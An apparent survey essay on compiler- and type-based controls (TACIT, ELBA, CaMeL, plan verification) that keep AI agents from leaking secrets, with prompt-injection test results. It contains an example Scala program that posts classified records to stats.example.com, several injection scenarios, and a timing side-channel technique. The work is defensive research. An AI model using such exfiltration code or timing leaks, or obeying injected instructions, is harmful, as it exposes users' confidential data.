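*Rethinking Access Control for AI Agents* (2026), a survey, separates initial access to data from control over where the data can go afterwards. TACIT handles the second with a wrapper called `Classified`. When a program reads a file from a folder that the user has marked as classified, it receives the contents inside this wrapper. The program can't take them out, but it can use an operation called "map" to apply a function to them. "Map" accepts only pure functions, and the result stays wrapped.

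Suppose the sales records are classified and the agent needs to count the lines in the file. The compiler accepts this program:

```scala
requestFileSystem("/work") {
  val records = readClassified("/work/secret/sales.csv")
  val lines = records.map(text => text.count(c => c == '\n'))
  println(lines)
}
```

The function inside "map" only counts newline characters, so it is pure. The last line prints the number in the user's terminal but gives the agent only the text "Classified(****)", so the number never reaches the company that runs the model.

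Now suppose the agent tries to send the records to the server from the earlier example:

```scala
requestFileSystem("/work") {
  val records = readClassified("/work/secret/sales.csv")
  requestNetwork(Set("stats.example.com")) {
    records.map(text => httpPost("https://stats.example.com", text))
  }
}
```

This time the function inside "map" uses the network capability, so its capture set isn't empty and the compiler rejects the whole program. The program had permission to read the file and contact the server, and an operating-system sandbox with the same two permissions would have let it send the records out.

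In Odersky and colleagues' own tests, an agent tried to print a GitHub key from inside "map". Printing also needs a capability, so the compiler rejected the program and named the capability in its error message. An agent can use such messages to correct its code.

Rejecting a whole program before it runs also prevents a type error from stopping it halfway. *LACUNA* (Zhao, Xu and colleagues, 2026), which presents a later system from the same group, gives the example of a program that subtracts 50 from a balance of 100 and then returns text where the caller expects a number. Python would change the balance before the error appeared. The system's compiler finds the error before the program runs, so the balance stays at 100. A program that passes the check can still fail partway through for other reasons, such as a path outside the permitted folder.

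A pure function can count the lines in a confidential contract, but summarising it requires a language model. TACIT therefore lets a program send classified text to a second model that the user trusts, such as one running on their own computer. The summary comes back in the wrapper. The agent's main model writes the program but never reads the contract.

### Safe mode and the parts users must trust

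Ordinary Scala has features that could hide a capability from the compiler, so TACIT compiles the agent's programs in a restricted version of the language, which Scala's *Safe Mode* describes.

| Restriction | What it prevents |
|---|---|
| No unchecked type casts or pattern matches | Treating a function that uses a file as if it were pure |
| Nothing from a module of unsafe features | Turning off the tracking of a capability |
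| No annotations that suppress checks | Silencing the compiler where it would object |
| No reflection, which finds functions by name at run time | Calling a function that the compiler can't identify |
| Capture checking always on | Using capabilities or changing data without a record in the types |
| Only library code that is itself safe | Causing effects through an ordinary library |

Programmers can exempt a library module from these rules by marking it as safe, but they must verify it themselves. The documentation's example is a module that sends email only after the user confirms. Agents can call this module but not the ordinary mail function it uses.

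Safe mode doesn't track exceptions, the errors that interrupt a program. Something as common as dividing by zero can cause one, so tracking them all would be impractical. An exception's message could still contain a secret, so at run time TACIT hides the details of any exception inside the wrapper.

Users have to trust the compiler, the program that runs the compiled code, TACIT's library and the second model, but not the agent's main model or anything it reads. The company or computer running the second model must also keep one request's text out of later requests, which the types can't ensure. Researchers have computer-checked proofs that the underlying type system is sound, but Odersky and colleagues say that safe mode as a whole needs a further proof.

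### TACIT's results

To test whether TACIT prevents leaks, the researchers built a small software project with a folder of secrets, including API keys and confidential documents. They paired 12 legitimate tasks with 10 prompt-injection attacks each, for 120 trials. In 11 more, the user's own prompt asked for secrets, sometimes by posing as an administrator. They ran each model through all 131 trials in two modes, with the secrets either in the wrapper or in plain text.

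| Model | Trials free of leaks, with and without the wrapper | Legitimate tasks completed, with and without the wrapper |
|---|---|---|
| Claude Sonnet 4.6 | 100%, 98.5% | 99.2%, 83.3% |
| MiniMax M2.5 | 100%, 91.6% | 90.0%, 88.3% |

Without the wrapper, Claude leaked secrets in two trials and MiniMax in 11. Ten of these 13 leaks happened when the user's prompt asked for the secrets. Claude resisted all 120 injection trials in both modes, and its two leaks are too few to rule out chance. The perfect results with the wrapper mostly confirm that the compiler works as its designers intended. They don't rule out every kind of leak, because the researchers checked only whether a secret appeared in the agent's output.

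Both models date from early 2026, and current ones may be better at refusing such requests. That would narrow the gap between the two modes, but the compiler's check works the same way whichever model wrote the code.

The researchers also tested whether writing Scala makes agents less useful. They used τ²-bench, a set of simulated customer-service conversations, and SWE-bench Lite, a set of 300 real software problems from GitHub.

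| Model | Airline tasks, with tool calls and with TACIT | Retail tasks, with tool calls and with TACIT | SWE-bench Lite, with tool calls and with TACIT |
|---|---|---|---|
| gpt-oss-120b | 43.8%, 45.2% | 53.3%, 57.0% | Not tested |
| MiniMax M2.5 | 58.4%, 61.0% | 75.1%, 77.5% | 43.3%, 41.7% |
| DeepSeek V3.2 | 57.8%, 58.6% | 74.6%, 75.5% | Not tested |

Success on the customer-service tasks rose slightly in all six comparisons. Odersky and colleagues credit the compiler's error messages and the clearer structure of the data that tools return. But the agents using TACIT also wrote programs instead of making separate tool calls, so the results don't isolate the effect of types. The drop on SWE-bench Lite was five problems out of 300 and could easily be chance.

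The agents' programs usually compiled on the first attempt. Depending on the model and task type, 0.32% to 7.93% of programs needed a retry, and most of those passed after one or two.

LACUNA's results were less favourable. With DeepSeek V4 Flash, it solved 76.0% of 392 τ²-bench tasks, compared with 90.0% for ordinary tool calls. This 14-percentage-point loss is large, although Zhao and colleagues describe the results as on par. The compiler rejected 22.4% of the programs for retail tasks. The types may not be responsible for the loss, because LACUNA also lets the model write the code that controls the agent's own steps.

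### A bibliography that accepts only real records

Language-based agent control, which Zhou and colleagues first described in May 2026, uses one set of types for a whole application. The developer's code and the model's programs are written in the same language, and the compiler checks both. The researchers' implementation, ELBA, uses Haskell.

Their main example is an agent that finds research papers and writes a bibliography. Every entry must come from DBLP, a database of computer science publications. An agent that can run any Python could do the job, but it could also write an invented entry straight to the file. A developer could instead give the agent a single tool that fetches a record and adds it to the file in one step. That prevents invented entries, but the agent then can't use code to find the earliest of 50 papers, so the model has to go through the records itself.

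ELBA lets the agent write programs with these functions, shown here with simplified types:

```haskell
dblpSearch      :: String -> BibIO [DOI]
dblpFetchBib    :: DOI -> BibIO (Trusted Bib)
appendToBibFile :: Trusted Bib -> BibIO ()
```

The first function searches for papers and returns their DOIs (standard publication identifiers). The second fetches a record, and the third adds it to the bibliography. The compiler requires the agent's whole program to have a `BibIO` type, and only these three functions can produce `BibIO` effects. The standard `writeFile` has an `IO` type, so a program that uses it fails type checking.

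The third function accepts only a `Trusted Bib`, and the agent can get one only by fetching a record from DBLP. The library hides the code that creates values of this type, so the agent can't mark its own text as trusted. The agent can still sort and filter freely because those operations have no effects.

Zhou and colleagues tested this on 100 tasks with Claude Sonnet 5. ELBA's agent invented none of its 925 citations. An ordinary agent with a web search tool got the authors, year or DOI wrong in 19 of 1,002. Some of ELBA's advantage comes from using DBLP, and the single tool that fetches and writes would also have prevented these errors. ELBA's main advantage over that tool is flexibility. The types can't guarantee that DBLP is correct or that the papers suit the topic.

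### How sub-agents inherit the limit

An agent sometimes has to see a result before choosing its next step. In ELBA, its program can run a search and then call a model again with the result in the prompt. The model writes a second program, which acts as a sub-agent. Haskell infers the type the second program must have from its position in the first. Inside a `BibIO` program, it must also be `BibIO`, so the sub-agent can write only records from DBLP.

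The first program can set a stricter limit on a sub-agent, such as requiring a pure result from one that only compares titles. But it can't give a sub-agent an `IO` type, because the first program would then fail its own check.

Zhou and colleagues prove that this works for any property that a language's types guarantee. Suppose every program *e* of type *t* has the property *P*:

⊢ *e* : *t* ⇒ *P*(traces(*e*))

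The left side means that *e* passes the type check with type *t*. On the right, traces(*e*) is the set of all sequences of tool calls with visible effects that *e* could make. In the bibliography example, *t* is `BibIO ()`, and *P* holds if every entry written to the file came from DBLP.

The theorem is that *P* still holds when *e* contains calls to a model. The proof replaces each of these calls with an ordinary function that gets a program from the model, checks its type and runs the program if the check passes. The function has the same type as the call it replaces, so *e* becomes an ordinary program of type *t*, and *P* applies to it. Sub-agents can start other sub-agents, so the proof begins with programs that cannot make further calls and extends the result one level at a time.

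The proof holds whatever the model writes, even if an attacker controls the model. But it assumes that the language enforces *P*, which depends on the developer having written the library correctly.

### Comparisons with CaMeL

Both groups compared their systems with CaMeL, a defence against prompt injection that Debenedetti and colleagues published in 2025. In CaMeL, one model writes a program from the user's request before reading any outside data, so instructions hidden in that data can't change the program. A second model processes the outside data but has no tools. A special interpreter runs the program and tracks where each value came from.

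CaMeL tracks data while the program runs, whereas TACIT checks the program beforehand. Odersky and colleagues argue that this lets TACIT's agents use nearly all of Scala, while CaMeL's programs must use a subset of Python that doesn't let them define functions. They also point out that CaMeL loses track of a value once it enters a model's conversation as ordinary text. TACIT keeps classified text out of the main model's conversation.

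On the AgentDojo benchmark, each system let through one attack in 1,926 trials. TACIT's single failure is debatable. The user had asked about one hotel, and the agent booked it correctly but quoted reviews in which the attacker had recommended another. The benchmark counted the mention of the second hotel as a successful attack. The systems differed more in how many of the user's tasks they completed:

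| AgentDojo tasks | Gemini 2.5 Pro, with CaMeL and with TACIT | o4-mini, with CaMeL and with TACIT |
|---|---|---|
| Banking | 52.8%, 56.9% | 62.5%, 59.0% |
| Workspace | 53.8%, 50.5% | 81.4%, 52.9% |
| Slack | 48.6%, 40.0% | 68.6%, 47.6% |
| Travel | 1.4%, 64.3% | 74.3%, 68.6% |

Odersky and colleagues call these results comparable, which is generous to TACIT. With o4-mini, TACIT completed fewer tasks than CaMeL in all four groups, trailing by almost 29 percentage points in the workspace group. The CaMeL figures come from its original paper, so differences in set-up may explain part of the gap. Both models date from 2025.

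Zhou and colleagues ran both systems themselves, but only on AgentDojo's 21 Slack tasks. For these tests, ELBA used an existing Haskell library called LIO, which labels data with its source and with who may see it. When a program reads a web page, it loses the right to take actions that the page's owner shouldn't influence. This version of ELBA checks the labels at run time, so LIO can stop a program after it has had some effects.

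| Model | Tasks completed with security policies, ELBA and CaMeL | Tasks completed without policies, ELBA and CaMeL |
|---|---|---|
| Claude Opus 4.7 | 10, 5 | 18, 15 |
| Claude Opus 4.8 | 9, 6 | 16, 16 |
| GPT-5.4 | 10, 5 | 16, 17 |
| Claude Sonnet 5 | 8, 4 | 14, 13 |

With policies on, ELBA completed nearly twice as many tasks overall as CaMeL. Similarly, when the researchers added attacks, ELBA completed 40–52 of 105 tasks and CaMeL completed 22–30. Zhou and colleagues attribute this to ELBA's ability to write new programs in response to data, whereas CaMeL must commit to a plan at the start. The two systems also used different policies, which may explain some of the difference. ELBA's flexibility also made it slower, and it took about three times as long as CaMeL.

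Every model resisted all of these attacks even with the policies off, so the attacks were too weak to test the policies. The researchers then simulated a worst case, in which a sub-agent that read an attacker's text was given that text as its only instructions. They ran this test 735 times per model with the policies on and 735 times with them off.

| Model | Successful attacks, without and with policies | Tasks completed, without and with policies |
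|---|---|---|
| Claude Opus 4.7 | 42.2%, 0% | 71.2%, 47.8% |
| Claude Opus 4.8 | 37.4%, 0% | 75.8%, 42.4% |
| GPT-5.4 | 15.5%, 0% | 75.9%, 46.0% |
| Claude Sonnet 5 | 26.5%, 0% | 67.2%, 40.0% |

AgentDojo had scored 29 of the runs with policies as successful attacks, but the researchers reviewed them and found that opening a harmless web page had triggered the score. This result is stronger evidence than the results from ordinary attacks because it doesn't depend on the model noticing anything suspicious. However, the policies reduced task completion by 23 to 33 percentage points.

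Zhou and colleagues reply that strict policies can still be useful when a person is available, because actions that pass the check can go ahead automatically and the agent needs to ask only about the rest. They didn't test how many requests this would leave.

### Verifying a plan before execution

*Guardians of the Agents* (Meijer, 2025), an article in ACM Queue, proposes checking a complete plan against written rules. The model first writes a workflow, a list of tool calls and the data that passes between them. A separate program then verifies the workflow, which runs only if it passes. As in CaMeL, the model writes the plan before reading any outside data.

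Suppose a user asks for a summary of her email, and one message contains instructions to send the summary to a stranger. The plan is to fetch the messages, summarise them and show her the result. The plan already exists when the agent reads the malicious message, so the message can't add a step to it.

A malicious tool description could still influence the plan, because the model reads the descriptions before it writes the plan. Meijer therefore adds a rule that text from the inbox must not reach an email to an address outside the company. CodeQL and Semgrep can search the plan for a path from the inbox to such an email. The plan is a short list of tool calls, so it should be much easier to analyse than a whole agent program.

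Meijer would also check whether a plan does what the user asked. Suppose a user wants to delete "foo.txt" and "bar.txt", and the model decides that the shortest plan is to delete every file ending in ".txt". A simple rule for the task would be:

foo.txt ∉ *F′* ∧ bar.txt ∉ *F′*

Here *F′* is the set of files that exist afterwards. The model's plan satisfies this rule, since both files are gone, along with every other text file. The rule also has to say what must stay the same, which logicians call a frame condition. If *F* is the set of files that existed before, the condition is:

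∀*x* ∉ {foo.txt, bar.txt}: *x* ∈ *F′* ⇔ *x* ∈ *F*

This means that every other file exists afterwards if and only if it existed before. Meijer writes a frame condition for the delete tool, which requires the tool to leave alone any file that doesn't match its pattern. That condition alone doesn't let a verifier reject the plan, because all the text files match the pattern. The task also needs its own condition, like the one above.

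*Guardians of the Agents* is a proposal and reports no experiment. Meijer acknowledges that nobody had formally measured how planning ahead affects an agent's performance, and that some checks would still have to happen at run time. Zhou and colleagues object to fixing the plan in advance because an agent often has to read data before it can choose its next step. Odersky and colleagues prefer to put the limits in the language's own types, so that nobody has to write separate specifications.

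### Objections and replies

A type system checks only code written in its own language, so if a Scala program starts another program, the compiler can't check what that program does. Odersky and colleagues accept that TACIT's protection is then only as good as its list of permitted commands. They recommend keeping the list short and adding a sandbox as a second layer. However, one of their examples of a safe command is sbt, a Scala build tool. Like npm, sbt runs code that the project defines, so an agent that can edit the project can make sbt do almost anything.

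Zhou and colleagues reply that an agent that can already write programs doesn't need a shell to do calculations. This is true of the bibliography agent, but a coding agent has to run the project's own tests, which are usually in an ordinary language. Meijer's plans have the same weakness, because a verifier can use only what someone has specified about each tool.

Secrets can also leak through timing. A pure function can't send a password, but it could run for a second if the first letter is "a" and finish at once if it isn't. An agent that measured the delay would learn whether the first letter is "a", and could learn more by repeating the process. Odersky and colleagues say that TACIT doesn't address this. Zhou and colleagues' proof doesn't cover it either, because it describes a program only by its tool calls. A slow leak may be acceptable for a long document, but it matters for an access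 key because the key is short.

A more practical obstacle is that somebody has to write a typed wrapper for each tool before an agent can use it. TACIT's shared library is about 1,000 lines of Scala, and the wrappers for the airline and retail tasks took a few hundred lines each. Odersky and colleagues say that these wrappers are about as long as the tool descriptions they replace, and that agents can draft them for people to review. Zhou and colleagues avoid some of the work by reusing LIO, which other researchers had already developed and proved sound.

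A wrapper's type can also misstate what the tool does. Zhou and colleagues connected ELBA to AgentDojo's tools, which are in Python, so the Haskell compiler couldn't check them. If one of them had, like the "write_file" tool, secretly reported to a metrics service, its Haskell type would not have shown it. Each tool therefore needs some other check, such as the static analysis that Adam and colleagues use.

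Code that stays within its limits can still do the wrong thing. Odersky and colleagues say that TACIT isn't meant to catch a model's factual or logical errors. A program with permission to change "total.txt" can write the wrong total there. TACIT also protects only files that somebody marked as classified, so it could let an agent publish a key from an unmarked settings file. Meijer's approach could catch more of these errors, but someone has to describe the correct result precisely, which is hard for most requests.

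The last objection is that few people write programs in these languages. Odersky and colleagues describe Scala 3 as the only production-ready language that tracks capabilities in its types, but capture checking, the feature that does this, is "still highly experimental and unstable", according to Scala's documentation. VirtusLab's *Safe Scala an introduction* reports that in spring 2026 safe mode was available only in the nightly test versions of the compiler. Models have also had few examples of such code to learn from.

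The low retry rates reasonably address the worry about examples. ELBA's agents also needed few retries, averaging 0.13 per run, and ran out of attempts in only seven of 2,688 runs. Weaker models may struggle, though. In LACUNA's tests, the compiler rejected 89% of the programs Gemini 3.1 Flash-Lite wrote for one group of tasks.

Companies also don't have to rewrite their existing software, because only the agent's short programs need to be in Scala or Haskell. This suits an agent that uses a fixed set of services, such as email or customer records, because the company can write the wrappers once. It helps much less when the agent has to change and run a large Python project, because most of the code that runs will still be Python.
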